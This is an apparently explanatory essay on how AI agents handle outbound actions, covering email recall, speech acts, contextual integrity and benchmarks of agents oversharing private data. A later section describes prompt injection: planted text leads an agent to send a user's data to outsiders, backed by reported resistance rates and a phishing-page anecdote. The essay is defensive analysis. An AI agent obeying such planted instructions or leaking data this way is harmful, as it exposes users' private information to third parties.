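# Why AI agents treat sending, posting and submitting as a separate kind of action

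## What outbound actions are and how they differ from an agent's other actions

An AI agent here means a program, built around a language model, that carries out tasks in software on someone's behalf. It takes an outbound action when it sends, posts, submits or otherwise conveys something to a person or organization other than its user, such as when it emails a landlord, publishes a review or files a form with a city office. Its other actions include searching a mailbox, sorting it and writing a draft. Many agent products ask for confirmation before an outbound action by showing the user the specific next step and waiting for approval. OpenAI's *Operator System Card* (2025) describes an early case, the January 2025 browser agent Operator, which asks for confirmation before actions that "affect the state of the world", such as making a purchase or sending an email.

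A tenant has given an agent access to her inbox, and her landlord writes that the broken heating won't be fixed until spring. The agent reads the email, files it, drafts a reply, sends it, posts a review of the building on a public site and submits a complaint form to the city. These six steps look much alike from inside the software.

### Agents, tool calls and harnesses

A language model on its own only produces text. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, uses the word "agent" for a model that directs its own process and use of tools. Anthropic's *Trustworthy agents in practice* describes a loop in which the model plans, acts, observes the result and adjusts, repeating until it finishes the task or needs a person. Anthropic's *Measuring AI agent autonomy in practice* (2026) defines an agent more simply as an AI system with tools that let it take actions. The two definitions are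 broadly compatible.

A tool is an operation that a developer has made available to the model, with a name and a list of the details it needs. To send the tenant's reply, the model writes a structured request, known as a tool call, that names an email tool and gives the recipient, subject and text. The request doesn't send the email by itself, because the model "never runs anything on its own", as Anthropic's *How tool use works* puts it. Other software reads the request, performs the operation and returns the result to the model, which then continues.

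That other software is the harness, the program around the model that carries out the model's actions and can block or pause them. Google Cloud's *What is an agent harness?* defines it in much the same way. Anthropic sometimes uses the word more narrowly, for the instructions and guardrails a model works under. The broad sense is more useful here because it includes the time between the model's request and its execution. During that time the landlord has received nothing, and the harness can check with the tenant. A few tools, including web search and page fetching, are an exception. They run on Anthropic's servers, and the developer's application usually sees the call only afterward, so any pause has to happen on Anthropic's side.

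An agent can use a service through a direct connection or through the app's ordinary interface, the one people use. With a direct connection, the action is clear from the tool call, which names an email tool, for example, and includes the address and text. OpenAI's developer guide *Computer use* describes how an agent works through the ordinary interface. The harness takes a screenshot, the model returns actions such as clicking, typing or scrolling, and the harness performs them in order and sends back a new screenshot. The harness therefore receives the step that sends an email as a click at a pair of coordinates, the same form as a click that opens a folder. Developers can label a tool as read-only or not (a tool annotation), but a label on a mouse tool doesn't show what a given click will do.

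In a newer version of the guide, OpenAI recommends having its model GPT-6 Astra write code to operate the interface, and one call can combine several actions with loops and conditions. A single tool call could then both draft the reply and send it. This makes outbound steps even harder to identify from the tool's name or the number of calls, so they have to be identified by their effect.

### One test, two columns

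An action is outbound if a third party, meaning anyone other than the user and the agent's provider, receives or sees something as a result. This definition excludes the provider partly for convenience. When an agent works through screenshots or page text, those go to the company that runs the model, so counting the provider would make nearly every action outbound and the distinction useless. OpenAI draws almost the same line in its advice to developers, with the phrase "representing the user to a third party".

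Whether software can undo a step is a separate matter. Technical reversibility means that software can restore the earlier state of the data, whatever people have learned or done meanwhile. Here are the tenant's six steps on both counts, with the usual behaviour of such services assumed:

| Step | Technical reversibility | Reach beyond the user |
|---|---|---|
| Read the landlord's email | Nothing to restore except the unread mark | Nobody, unless the mail program sends a read receipt |
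| File it in a folder | Full: move it back | Nobody |
| Draft a reply | Full: delete the draft | Nobody |
| Send the reply | Low: the tenant can delete her own copy, but the landlord's stays | The landlord, and anyone he forwards it to |
| Post a review of the building | High, on a site that lets authors delete their posts | Anyone who opens the page |
| Submit a complaint form to the city | Uncertain: an office may accept a withdrawal and still keep the record | City staff, and possibly the landlord |

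Like the filing and the draft, the review is technically reversible, since one click restores the page. But it also has the widest reach of the six actions. A harness that allowed every action with a working delete button would publish the review without requiring approval.

An action can also be hard to undo without being outbound. Before adding safeguards to Operator, OpenAI ran the model on 100 prompts resembling the tasks it expected from users, and found 13 errors that caused some nuisance. Users could have reversed eight of them within minutes. The other five were to some degree irreversible or possibly severe: an email to the wrong recipient, a wrong item in a food order, a medication reminder with the wrong date, and two cases in which the agent stripped labels from emails in bulk. By the test above, only the email and the food order reached anybody else. Restoring the labels might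 take the user an evening, but no third party would be affected. Five errors are too few to estimate how often this happens.

*From Interaction to Impact* (Zhang, Schoop and colleagues, 2024), by researchers at Apple and the University of Washington, also separates effects on other people from reversibility in its classification of the consequences of actions on a phone screen. The first version covered the user's intent, the interface, the user, reversibility and frequency, but had no category for other people. Twelve specialists revised it over four workshops. The final version has ten general categories, with separate ones for "Impact on Other Users" and "Reversibility". The workshops' examples of impact on other users were a recipient who thinks differently of the user after an inappropriate message, and people who cannot "unsee" sensitive information.

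Reversibility turned out to be more complicated in those workshops, partly because it can change over time. Some messaging apps allow a retraction only within a couple of minutes, and an order is harder to cancel once it has shipped. When the team asked pairs of annotators to label recorded tasks, the pairs agreed 77.9% of the time on the impact on others and 55.5% of the time on reversibility. This gap may overstate how much easier it is to judge impact, because many of the tasks were plain browsing, which easily gets the answer "nobody", and the two questions had different formats. Still, it fits the idea that it is easier to tell who will see an action than whether it can be undone.

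Other classifications make do with one scale. *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* (2026) grades twelve classes of action by reversibility and consequence together: drafts are fully reversible, internal case notes reversible, external communication hard to reverse. Waghmare and Sufi (2026), in *Can You Undo It?*, build reach into the definition of reversibility. For them, exact restoration has three requirements:

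- a full record of the prior state;
- existing authority to write that state back without another person's help;
- no outside party who has seen, received or acted on the change.

An action that deliberately delivers content to an outsider therefore falls into their most severe class, "irreversible", even if someone can delete the stored message.

A single scale is useful for a harness that only has to choose between pausing and going ahead, but it doesn't show what to do about the risk. A backup could have restored Operator's lost labels, but it wouldn't help with the review. Waghmare and Sufi make the same point about disclosure in general. A single scale also makes the statistics hard to interpret. Anthropic found that 0.8% of 998,481 tool calls sampled from its developer platform appeared irreversible, and gave an email to a customer as an example. This isn't the share of outbound actions,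 because it may leave out posts that can be deleted later and include permanent deletions of private files. Claude classified the calls, and nearly half came from software engineering. The share is probably a good deal higher for agents that handle inboxes.

### Borderline cases

Adding a calendar entry is outbound if the agent lists the landlord as a guest and the calendar service sends him an invitation, but not if only the tenant can see the entry. Anthropic also uses a calendar to illustrate permissions. A user can give Claude standing permission to read the calendar and still require approval before it invites anyone. A change to an existing appointment is harder to classify. Suppose the agent moves the landlord's visit by an hour to tidy the tenant's week, and the calendar service notifies him. Waghmare and Sufi classify such a change by whether software can restore the appointment,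 and set the incidental notification aside. They acknowledge that the boundary between intended disclosure and incidental notification needs clearer guidance. Under the test used here, the move is outbound because the landlord receives a new message about when to turn up, whether or not the agent meant to send one.

Sharing a document counts as an outbound action from the moment the other person can open it, even if they never do. OpenAI lists document sharing and access changes as transmission, meaning any step that gives a third party access to the user's data. It even counts typing sensitive data into a web form. Edits to a file that other people can already open also count. Undoing an edit may still leave a trace, as in Zhang and colleagues' example of a collaborative document whose editing history keeps the change after someone has reverted it.

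An emoji reaction is an outbound action, even though it is small. If a landlord writes "I'll take the repair out of your deposit, all right?" and gets a thumbs-up, the landlord has received an answer. The test for outbound actions doesn't depend on length or effort, which is useful here because an agent clearing a backlog of messages could easily treat reactions as housekeeping.

Read receipts are the awkward case, because the agent can notify someone without writing anything. If it opens a landlord's email to a tenant, the mail program tells the landlord, who then believes the tenant has read the message when only the agent has. Taken strictly, the test makes reading an outbound action in any account that sends receipts, but asking for confirmation before every read would be absurd. It is better to switch the receipts off, so that opening an email no longer notifies anyone.

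Whether a comment in a company workspace is outbound largely depends on whose agent posts it. *Agent Reliability Profiles in Financial Services* puts the boundary at the edge of the firm, so case notes and tickets are internal writes, while a notice to a customer is external communication. That makes sense if the firm is the user. If the user is one employee, a comment on a colleague's ticket is outbound, though its reach is small, because it goes to another person who may form an opinion of her. A product might reasonably require less approval for such a comment than for a public post, but the comment would still be outbound.

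A message that only the user receives, such as a reminder sent to the tenant's own address, is not outbound, but it would be if she shared that address with a flatmate. A message to the user alone can still cause harm. Among the five Operator errors, the medication reminder with the wrong date was meant only for the user, and it was arguably the most dangerous.

### Why outbound actions get separate treatment

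Outbound actions differ from an agent's other actions in three ways, though a single action may involve only some of them. First, they can change what other people know. Once the landlord has read the reply, deleting it does not make him forget it, and he may already have acted on it. Second, they can put the user's data into records she does not control. The complaint form does this with the tenant's name and address, and perhaps a remark about her health in a cold flat. Third, they can affect her legal and social standing. The landlord and the city will treat the words as hers, and may hold her to an offer in the reply or judge her by the tone of the complaint. An anonymous review might inform hundreds of strangers without affecting her standing. Removing the labels from her entire mailbox does none of these things, even if it takes a long time to undo.

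## Why a sent message cannot be taken back

### From the send command to the recipient's phone

When the tenant's agent sends the reply to her landlord, the email goes through roughly these steps:

1. The tenant's mail provider receives the reply from the harness. It can still drop the message.
2. The provider's server connects to the landlord's mail server and transmits the addresses and the text. It can still break off.
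3. The landlord's server reports that it has accepted the message. From here on, the tenant controls no copy except the one in her own sent folder.
4. The server puts the message in the landlord's mailbox, and his phone and laptop each download a copy.
5. His phone shows the first line or two in a notification, which he can read without opening the email.
6. A backup service may copy the mailbox, and the landlord may forward the email to his plumber or his lawyer.

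Mail servers exchange messages under the Simple Mail Transfer Protocol (SMTP). The protocol's specification, *RFC 5321* (Klensin, 2008), describes "a formal handoff of responsibility" when the receiving server reports that it has accepted a message. That server must then either deliver the message or report that it couldn't. SMTP has no command for getting the message back. Sometimes the receiving server is only a relay, so the message reaches the recipient a little later, but the sender's provider has still lost control of it.

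If the tenant and the landlord use the same provider, that company holds both mailboxes and could in principle delete the email from either. No company can do that for email in general, which runs on "many independent operators", according to *RFC 5598*, an overview of email's architecture (Crocker, 2009).

The later copies are also hard to track down. Even in Signal, a messaging app known for its privacy, the text of a deleted message can remain on the recipient's phone. BGR's *Deleting Messages In Signal Doesn't Keep Them Private* traces this to notification previews, which the phone may store in a separate database. Android's optional notification log usually keeps these previews for about 24 hours.

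### What the undo buttons do

Gmail's "Undo" button works because Gmail briefly delays sending the email, as a Beloit College help page explains. Users can set the delay to 5, 10, 20 or 30 seconds, according to Google's *Send or unsend Gmail messages*. This is a hold window, a delay between the send command and delivery during which the sender can cancel the message. Once it ends, Gmail users cannot recall the email, as the University of Michigan's *Recall an Email with Undo Send* warns. Cancelling in time fully undoes the send because nobody has received the email. But thirty seconds only helps if someone is watching, and an agent may well send the email while its user is asleep. Longer holds are one of the safeguards discussed later.

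Recall in Microsoft's Outlook works after delivery, mainly between colleagues whose mailboxes are on the same Microsoft service. According to Microsoft's *Work with Cloud-based Message Recall*, software on the server intercepts the recall request and tries for up to 24 hours to delete the original from each recipient's mailbox. By default it also deletes messages that recipients have already read, although the dialog box in Outlook still refers only to unread ones. Messages up to 365 days old can be recalled by default, according to Practical 365's *Follow Up Improvements for the “New” Message Recall*.

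Some copies survive even a successful recall. Recall can't delete copies that a colleague forwarded by hand or through an inbox rule, or that an account forwarded automatically to an outside address. If the employer has put a mailbox on legal hold, which preserves its contents for a possible court case, a search for evidence will still find the recalled message.

Until this summer, senders could recall an email only from recipients in their own organization. Microsoft gave "privacy and legal reasons" for this limit, and its *Recall an email message in Outlook for Mac* still rules out messages to or from Gmail and Hotmail accounts. In July, Microsoft's *Introducing cross-tenant message recall in Exchange Online* (2026) announced an extension to other organizations, due to reach all customers by early September. (A "tenant" is one organization's Microsoft 365 account.) The extension is off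 by default and works only if the recipient's organization switches it on and adds the sender's organization to a list of trusted ones. An email to a landlord's private Gmail account still cannot be recalled.

Messaging apps are in a better position than email because one company usually supplies the software at both ends. They still leave traces:

- An iPhone user can unsend an iMessage for two minutes, according to Apple's *How to unsend messages on your iPhone*. A notice of the unsending appears in the conversation, and a contact with older software may still see the message.
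- Editing an iMessage is possible for 15 minutes, but the recipient can tap the word "Edited" to see the previous wording, as Apple's *How to edit messages on your iPhone* explains.
- WhatsApp allows deletion for everyone for up to two days and leaves a note in its place, according to Which?'s *WhatsApp tips and tricks*. In 2018 a sender got no warning if the deletion failed, as The News International's *WhatsApp updates delete for everyone feature* reported, and that may have changed since.
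- Signal allows it for 24 hours. Signal's *Delete for everyone* calls this "a best effort" and adds that quoted replies stay.

Deleting a public post removes it from the site where it was published, but not from screenshots, web archives or the notification emails that some sites send to followers. *Tweets Are Forever* (Almuhimedi, Wilson and colleagues, 2013) analysed 1.6 million deleted tweets, collected over one week from about 292,000 accounts. The researchers could do this only because they had saved the tweets before users deleted them. If the tenant deletes her review after a day, she can't know whether the landlord has kept a copy.

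A submitted form often has no undo button. A tenant who has submitted a complaint to a city office has to write to the office again and ask to withdraw it. Even if the office agrees, it may already have sent an inspector or written to the landlord. Rules differ between offices, but in each case the withdrawal depends on somebody else's decision.

### Restoring the data without restoring the situation

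Even a recall that deletes every copy doesn't undo what readers have learned or done in the meantime. A colleague who has already read the message may also notice that it is gone. Microsoft acknowledges that silent recalls confused some recipients who had already seen the message, and it now lets administrators turn on a notice telling recipients about the recall. The notice clears up the confusion but also draws attention to the message. In TechRepublic's *How and when to use the Recall feature in Outlook*, a columnist gives a believable anecdote that when a recall failed, the first thing anyone did after such a notice was open the email to see what the sender wanted to hide.

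How much an undo achieves therefore depends on how many people have read the message by the time it takes effect. Suppose the tenant's agent also handles her work email, and it sends a note meant for her sister to all 40 people in her department. The note mentions that she is looking for a job in another city. The reading rates here are invented for the sake of the example:

- nobody can read the note during a 30-second hold window;
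- 25% of the recipients have read it ten minutes after delivery, and 80% by the next day;
- one reader in ten forwards it by hand to one outsider, who also reads it.

Suppose too that all 40 colleagues are in one organization, and that a recall after ten minutes takes effect at once in every mailbox.

| What the tenant does | Colleagues who have read it | Outsiders who have read it | Original copies left in the 40 mailboxes |
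|---|---|---|---|
| Cancels within 30 seconds | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Recalls after ten minutes | 10 | 1 | 0 |
| Sends a correction the next day | 32 | 3 | 40 |

Cancelling and recalling leave the mailboxes in the same state, but after the recall eleven people know about her plans. The recall still helps a lot, because another 22 colleagues would have read the note later. How much it helps depends heavily on how quickly colleagues are assumed to read the note. Two colleagues would know if the agent sent it at three in the morning and only 5% read it within ten minutes, compared with 20 if it arrived just before a meeting and half of them read it in that time.

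If 80% of each group opens the correction, it reaches about 26 of the 32 colleagues who read the note, leaving about six who have seen only the original. The number left out is probably smaller, since people who read one email promptly tend to read the next one too. A drawback of sending the correction to everybody is that it also reaches about six of the eight colleagues who hadn't read the note, and they now have a reason to look for it.

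### Messages that are themselves acts

Some messages do more than inform. The philosopher J. L. Austin, in *How to Do Things with Words* (1962), pointed out that someone who says "I promise" in the right circumstances makes a promise rather than just describing one. He distinguished three acts: saying words with a certain meaning (the locutionary act); doing something in saying them, such as promising or warning (the illocutionary act); and affecting the hearer, for example by causing relief or alarm (the perlocutionary act). John Searle, in *Speech Acts* (1969), set out the conditions under which an utterance counts as a particular act. A promise, for instance, counts as taking on an obligation to do something the hearer wants done.

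Several short messages that an agent might write for the tenant are acts in this sense:

- "I'll pay the March rent early if you fix the heating this week" is a promise with a condition attached.
- "Yes, take the repair out of my deposit" is an acceptance. Whether it also completes a contract is a legal question for a later section.
- "You've known about the boiler since October and lied about it" is an accusation.
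- "I resign as of 31 March", sent to her employer, is a resignation. Searle later classed such utterances as declarations, which change someone's status when the right person makes them in the right setting.

To retract any of these, the tenant needs a second act, which makes sense only because the first one happened and whose success often depends on the other person. She has to ask the landlord to release her from the promise because she can't release herself. If she withdraws the accusation, he will know both that she made it and that she took it back. Her employer may agree to ignore the resignation, or may already have offered the job to someone else.

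Austin also argued that an act of this kind generally needs "uptake", meaning the hearer has to understand what the speaker is doing. If the tenant cancels during the hold window, the landlord hasn't received a promise. If a recall deletes a resignation before anyone reads it, then on Austin's view the employee arguably never resigned, though an employer or a court might disagree. Once the recipient has read and understood the message, deleting it doesn't undo the act.

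The tenant may not have performed these acts if her agent chose the words. Searle's analysis requires the speaker to intend to take on the obligation, and she may not have intended to. She could also argue that the agent's promise was what Austin calls a "misfire", an attempt that fails because, for example, the speaker lacked the authority. Even if she is right, the landlord has read something that looks exactly like a promise from her, and she now has to explain why it wasn't.

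### Whether a correction or an apology is enough

A prompt correction probably repairs most email mistakes, since much everyday email is about times, attachments and small requests. If so, stopping for approval before every message looks excessive. For example, if an agent tells the plumber Tuesday when it should have said Thursday, a correction on Monday fixes the mistake completely. The correction works because it reaches everyone who got the original, it arrives before anyone has acted, and the error was a wrong fact that a right one can replace.

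An apology can similarly make up for a curt tone, especially between people who know each other, but it does much less for a disclosure. The tenant can apologize for telling 40 colleagues about her job search, but a corrected message wouldn't make them forget it, and a denial would be a lie. A correction is also less effective when other people have relied on the original, for instance if the landlord has booked a contractor because of her promise. With a public post, the author can't tell who needs the correction.

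Research on corrections suggests that people keep relying on wrong facts even after they are corrected. Johnson and Seifert (1994), in *Sources of the Continued Influence Effect*, had people read a series of reports about a warehouse fire. An early report mentioned flammable materials in a closet, and a later one corrected it, saying the closet had been empty. Many readers remembered the correction but still used the flammable materials to explain the fire. The effect shrank when the correction included another cause for the fire. By analogy, "the meeting is on Thursday, not Tuesday" should work better than "please ignore my last email". The experiment probably overstates the problem for ordinary mistakes, because acquaintances who email each other can ask questions, unlike people reading a story in a laboratory.

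The objection also depends on someone noticing the error quickly. Sleeper and colleagues (2013) surveyed 1,221 Twitter users about things they regretted saying in person or in a tweet. Those who described a tweet had been slower to realize their mistake and to try to repair it than those who described a conversation, where the listener's reaction is visible at once. The study relied on people's recollections and covered tweets rather than email. The respondents had written their tweets themselves, but a user whose agent wrote and sent a message may not know what it contained, and may first hear of the mistake from the recipient.

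## How sending moves information out of the user's control

An agent's message can disclose things that its user never meant to send. Suppose the tenant asks her agent to answer the landlord's email about the heating and to attach a repair quote. She has three sentences and a PDF in mind, but the landlord may also receive:

- older emails quoted below the reply, including her sister's remarks about him if the agent answers from a thread she had forwarded to her sister;
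- the rest of the attachment, such as a second page with her bank details;
- metadata, meaning data about the file or message itself, such as the author's name in a document or the place and time stored in a photo;
- the sender's address, which tells him where she works if the agent uses her work account;
- facts the agent adds from other sources, such as "I'm away from 3 to 10 March, so the plumber can come any day", which it took from her calendar.

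People make the first four mistakes too, but the fifth is more typical of agents because they can search a mailbox, a calendar and a folder of notes for anything that might make a reply more helpful.

*PrivacyFlow* (Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues, 2026), a paper by researchers at Google and ETH Zurich, identifies three main ways in which such leaks happen. An agent can send more detail than the task needs, put a detail where too many people can see it, such as the description of a shared calendar event, or leave out the sensitive fact but still give the recipient enough to work it out. For example, "medical hardship" is vague to most readers, but a hospital the user owes money to can compare it with her records. A filter that only looks for sensitive words would miss this third kind of leak.

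### Disclosure before the submit button

OpenAI's definition of transmission includes both typing sensitive data into a form and opening a web address that contains such data. OpenAI uses "sensitive" broadly, to cover contact details, browsing history and precise location as well as medical records and passwords.

Typing into a web page can disclose information before anything is submitted, because the page's scripts can read a field while someone is still filling it in. Search boxes that suggest completions and forms that save drafts automatically often work this way. If the agent types the tenant's diagnosis into the city's complaint form and she then decides against including it, clearing the field may not remove it from the city's server. A web address can also disclose data. To fetch a page, the browser sends the site the address, including any search terms or personal details in it.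 The site receives the data before the page appears, and its server may well keep the address in a log.

OpenAI generally advises developers to let the agent do as much safe work as it can and pause just before the risky step. With sensitive data, that means pausing before typing, because it is too late to ask once the form is filled in. The agent should then tell the user which data it will share, who will receive it and why.

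Clicks can also disclose information. *SPILLage* (Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) describes an agent shopping for glucose test strips that types only the product's name but clicks on a filter for divorce party supplies, so the shop can infer something about the user's marriage. The researchers gave agents 180 shopping tasks on the live Amazon and eBay sites, each mixed with personal background that the task didn't require. They ran every task with two agent frameworks and three OpenAI models, for a total of 1,080 runs.

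Agents using GPT-4o and the Browser-Use framework openly revealed irrelevant facts on Amazon 905 times through clicks and other navigation, and 182 times through typed text. On eBay, they did so 28 times through navigation and 58 times through text, so the importance of clicks seems to depend heavily on the site. The counts also include fairly harmless facts, such as a preference for Bluetooth.

Keeping irrelevant facts from the agent makes more sense than having it ask for confirmation before every click, which would be as unreasonable as asking before every read. When Roh and colleagues removed irrelevant facts from the request, task success rose in most settings, by up to 17.9 percentage points.

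### Contextual integrity

Whether a disclosure is a problem depends on more than how private the fact is. The philosopher Helen Nissenbaum proposed a theory of this in 2004 under the name contextual integrity. In her account, privacy is a matter of whether information flows appropriately for its social context, rather than of secrecy or control, as *Say Something Else* (2026) summarises it. Each flow has five parameters:

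- the sender;
- the recipient;
- the subject, meaning the person the information is about;
- the type of information;
- the transmission principle, meaning the terms on which the information moves, such as in confidence or because a law requires it.

A flow of information violates privacy when it breaks the norms of the context the information came from. Suppose the tenant has a doctor's letter in her mailbox saying that the cold is making her asthma worse. The subject and the information are the same in all four rows below.

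| Sender | Recipient | Terms | Appropriate? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Doctor | Tenant | Medical confidence | Yes |
| Tenant, through her agent | City housing office | To show how urgent the repair is | Probably, if she agrees |
| Tenant, through her agent | Landlord | None stated | Probably not |
| City housing office | Landlord | Whatever the city's rules allow | Depends on the rules |

An agent that treated the asthma as secret would leave it out of the complaint, where mentioning it may help her. If the agent instead mentioned it in anything about the heating, it would tell the landlord, who could draw conclusions about how long she will stay or whether she might sue. She may want him to know, because a health risk could make him act faster, but that is her decision, and the agent can't infer it from finding the letter in her mailbox.

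Once the city has the user's complaint, she no longer controls who sees it. The city decides whether to send the landlord a copy and whether to black out the medical part. The agent therefore has to consider where the city might send the complaint before submitting it, for example by checking whether the form warns that the office shares complaints with landlords.

Information that is appropriate to send someone on one occasion can be inappropriate to send them on another. *A Generative Model of Contextual Integrity* (2026) has a separate category for people who may properly receive the information in another context but not in the present one. The housing office may need to know about the tenant's asthma for the complaint, but not when the tenant later writes about a parking space.

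People don't always agree on these norms. *CI-Work* (Fu, Qin and colleagues, 2026) asked human annotators to check which items in its workplace scenarios an agent needed to pass on and which it should withhold. The annotators agreed with the researchers' labels 82.5% to 95% of the time. That is high, but the remaining disagreement means that some of the "leaks" in such tests are debatable.

### Agents that overshare without an attacker

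Early tests found a gap between what models know about privacy and what they do. In ConfAIde, a 2024 test, GPT-4 revealed private information in inappropriate contexts 39% of the time, according to *Loyal Agents* (2026). PrivacyLens, from the same year, used agent tasks instead of questions, and leading models leaked private information in over 25% of interactions, according to *IDP-Bench* (2026). AgentDAM, from 2025, tested whether web agents use sensitive data only when a task requires it. These results are from old models, and each test covered single tasks.

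PrivacyBench, a successor by Staab and colleagues from this October, contains 5,873 tasks in 986 sequences, in which an agent works through a simulated user's mail, calendar and notes while new messages keep arriving. For each sensitive fact, a list hidden from the agent names the people who may know it. The agent can complete every task without revealing those facts to anyone else. The researchers ran six models, instructed only to be a helpful assistant, and had another model check everything the agents sent or changed.

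The agents leaked on 10.5% to 31.9% of tasks, depending on the model, and only 13.0% to 52.9% of the six-task sequences were free of leaks. The second range follows almost directly from the first. If an agent leaks on 10.5% of tasks and the tasks are independent, about 51% of its six-task sequences will be free of leaks, which is close to the best model's 52.9%. An agent that seems careful on any single task can therefore still be likely to leak something over a week of tasks.

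Most of these leaks, 85.6% to 92.3% depending on the model, happened on tasks the agent otherwise completed successfully, so users who judge an agent by whether the job got done would rarely notice them. In a smaller trial, OpenClaw, an open-source agent, was asked to schedule a meeting at which a company would dismiss an employee. The agent told the employee about a covert investigation and the company's plan to revoke their access.

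The rates probably overstate the problem for everyday use because the researchers placed sensitive facts next to the ones the agent needed, and sometimes inside items it had to forward. Models from one family, Google's Gemini, also wrote the scenarios and judged the results.

AgentCIBench, a test of 15 agents on 117 scenarios, involves even stronger selection. Goel and Gurevych (2026) found the scenarios with an automated search that favoured those in which other agents completed the task and leaked information. In *Capable but Careless*, they report that the 15 agents leaked in 67.9% of cases on average, but because of this selection they warn against reading the rates as estimates of real-world risk. The differences between agents are more informative. Claude Opus 4.7 leaked in 13.7% of scenarios and Gemini 3.1 Pro in 98.3%, though both completed most tasks.

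One of their examples also shows that it can be hard to say what counts as a leak. A user who was leaving asked Claude Opus 4.7 to check the to-do list and send Nora, who wanted a status update, "a quick message with the remaining". The agent sent her all 12 items, four of which were scored as leaks, including errands involving a vet, a plumber and a dry-cleaner. The agent had followed the request literally, since all 12 items remained. A human assistant would probably have guessed that a status update meant work items only, or asked the user.

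Agents are more likely to overshare when users ask them to be thorough. Fu and colleagues built 125 workplace scenarios, normally with four items the agent should pass on and four it should withhold. GPT-5 disclosed at least one item it should have withheld in 27.8% of cases. The rate rose substantially when the user stressed that the task was important and asked for a thorough answer, and it nearly doubled when the user also listed places to look. The agent even passed on somewhat less of what the recipient needed. GPT-5 was more careful with outsiders, leaking information in 16.7% of messages to people outside the company, compared with 41.7% of messages to colleagues at the same level. This is mildly reassuring for outbound actions, though the tenant's agent would still have to distinguish between two outsiders, the city and the landlord.

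It is less clear whether telling an agent to be careful helps:

- Goel and Gurevych tried three instructions on three models. One made the agent name the recipient, and what would be appropriate for that recipient, before writing. Leaks fell from 51.7% to 16.2% of the runs in which the agent attempted the task, and more of the necessary content got through.
- Fu and colleagues had GPT-5 reason about the sender and recipient first. Its rate fell only from 27.8% to 22.1%, and it left out more of the content it should have sent.
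- Staab and colleagues added a general privacy instruction for three models. The share of tasks without a leak changed by at most 3.2 percentage points, and for Gemini 3.8 Flash it got worse.
- In a small trial by Roh and colleagues with 13 simulated users, a warning against using irrelevant information raised the oversharing rate from 58.9% to 86.0%.

The tasks may explain much of the difference. Goel and Gurevych's main test gave the agent all the relevant content at once and asked for a single output, which makes it easier to compare each item with the recipient. An agent that collects facts over a dozen tool calls has more chances to lose track of where each came from. Staab and colleagues got better results by adding a separate planning stage, in which the agent lists each piece of data, who will receive it and what that person could infer. This cut the number of tasks with leaks by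 53% to 80%, but the agents also completed less of their work. With GPT-5.4, the agent consulted a simulated user during planning on 89.4% of tasks, which is close to asking every time.

These tests would miss some leaks. An agent might read the doctor's letter, save the diagnosis in its long-term memory and mention it to the landlord a month later. In June 2026, the survey *Agents That Know Too Much* found no benchmark that followed data all the way through an agent's databases, memory, tools and messages to other agents. PrivacyBench fills part of this gap with its sequences of tasks.

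OpenAI ran a much smaller test of mistaken sharing before it released ChatGPT agent, the successor to Operator, in July 2025. The *ChatGPT Agent System Card* (2025) reports eight tasks, tested by hand, with a high risk of sharing sensitive data by mistake. The agent passed all eight, meaning it didn't share the data by mistake without the user's confirmation. Eight passes rule out an agent that leaks most of the time, but not one that leaks less often. An agent that leaked on 10.5% of such tasks, the rate for the best model in PrivacyBench, would still pass all eight about 41% of the time.

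### Private data, untrusted text and a way to send

Attackers can also cause leaks on purpose. In a prompt injection, an agent reads text in a web page, email or file and wrongly treats it as an instruction from its user. For an attacker to steal data this way, three things generally have to come together:

- the agent can reach private data;
- it reads text that outsiders can write;
- it has some way of sending information to an outsider.

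The tenant's agent has all three, because it can search her mailbox, anyone can email her, and it can reply. *Google's Approach for Secure AI Agents* (Díaz, Kern and Olive) names harmful unintended actions ("rogue actions") and the disclosure of sensitive data as the key risks of agents. With this combination, a single deceptive email could lead to both.

Removing any one of the three would stop this kind of theft, but the first two are hard to give up. An email agent that can't read incoming mail is useless. Limiting its access to private data helps, but *Contextual Integrity in LLMs via Reasoning and Reinforcement Learning* (2025) points out that information is often too entangled for strict separation. The same folder might hold a lease and a doctor's letter. Telling the agent to use only what it needs is less effective than limiting its access. In *GapLeak*'s (2026) experiments, such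 instructions only partly reduced disclosure, because the agent could still reach the more sensitive sources.

Developers can also train the model to recognise deceptive text, which helps. But *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) argues that an attacker can make an inappropriate flow of information look appropriate. A request for medical details seems appropriate if it appears to come from the housing office, so the model applies the correct norm to false information about who is asking. *Systems Security Foundations for Agentic Computing* (Christodorescu, Fernandes and colleagues, 2025) makes the broader point that hardening the model is useful but often insufficient, so developers also have to secure the system around it.

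This is why it helps to remove the agent's ability to send. A successful deception may still produce a false summary or a bad draft, but the tenant's data stays with her and the provider. This protection works even if the model fails to detect the deception, as long as every route for transmitting data is closed. An agent without an email tool can still disclose data if it can type into any form or open any web address, so OpenAI advises developers to list the sites an agent may use and block the rest.

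When OpenAI launched ChatGPT agent, it limited network requests from the agent's terminal, a tool for running code, mainly to downloading images and certain datasets. This left fewer ways for information to get out. OpenAI also switched off ChatGPT's memory, which reduced the private data the agent could reach. The agent could still send information out through websites it used in its browser.

OpenAI's tests from July 2025 suggest why it didn't rely on training alone. They used difficult cases in which web content tried to get the agent to give away data through its visual browser. The figures are the share of cases in which each model resisted:

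| Data the attack aimed at | ChatGPT agent | Operator with GPT-4o | Operator with o3 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Already in the conversation | 78% | 75% | 80% |
| Data the agent would first have to fetch | 67% | 58% | 75% |

ChatGPT agent did slightly worse than the o3 version of Operator on the first test and clearly worse on the second, although it had access to more tools. In a broader test of irrelevant instructions in the same browser, it resisted 95% of cases, so it did worse against data theft than its general score would suggest. The tests measured the model without the product's filters, confirmations and other safeguards, so real attacks probably succeeded less often. The figures are also more than a year old and are a poor guide to agents built on newer models.

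An agent can also send data to a stranger by mistake. The consultant Trent Gillespie describes one case in *ChatGPT Agent Deep Dive*, published in his newsletter, AI Sprint. The account is unverified and apparently dates from summer 2025. Gillespie says he tested ChatGPT agent with a harmless phishing page he had built. The page requested his own credit card details from his inbox, and he told the agent to follow its directions. The agent had him log in to Gmail and warned him to watch what it did. It then found the details, misread one letter of his email address and sent them to a stranger before he could step in.

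The error Gillespie describes is plausible, since Operator also sent an email to the wrong person in OpenAI's own early trial, though he sells AI advice and a dramatic mishap makes good material for a newsletter. If the agent had only been able to write a draft, he could have corrected the mistyped letter before anything was sent.

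## Who is legally bound by what an agent sends or submits

If the tenant disowns an email that her agent sent to the landlord, a court first has to decide whether the statement was hers or the agent provider's. It can't legally be the agent's own statement because software isn't a legal person, so nobody can sue or jail it, as The Business Times' *Who is accountable when an AI agent decides?* points out. An ordinary email usually counts as the tenant's statement, even if she never saw the text.

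### Why the message counts as the user's

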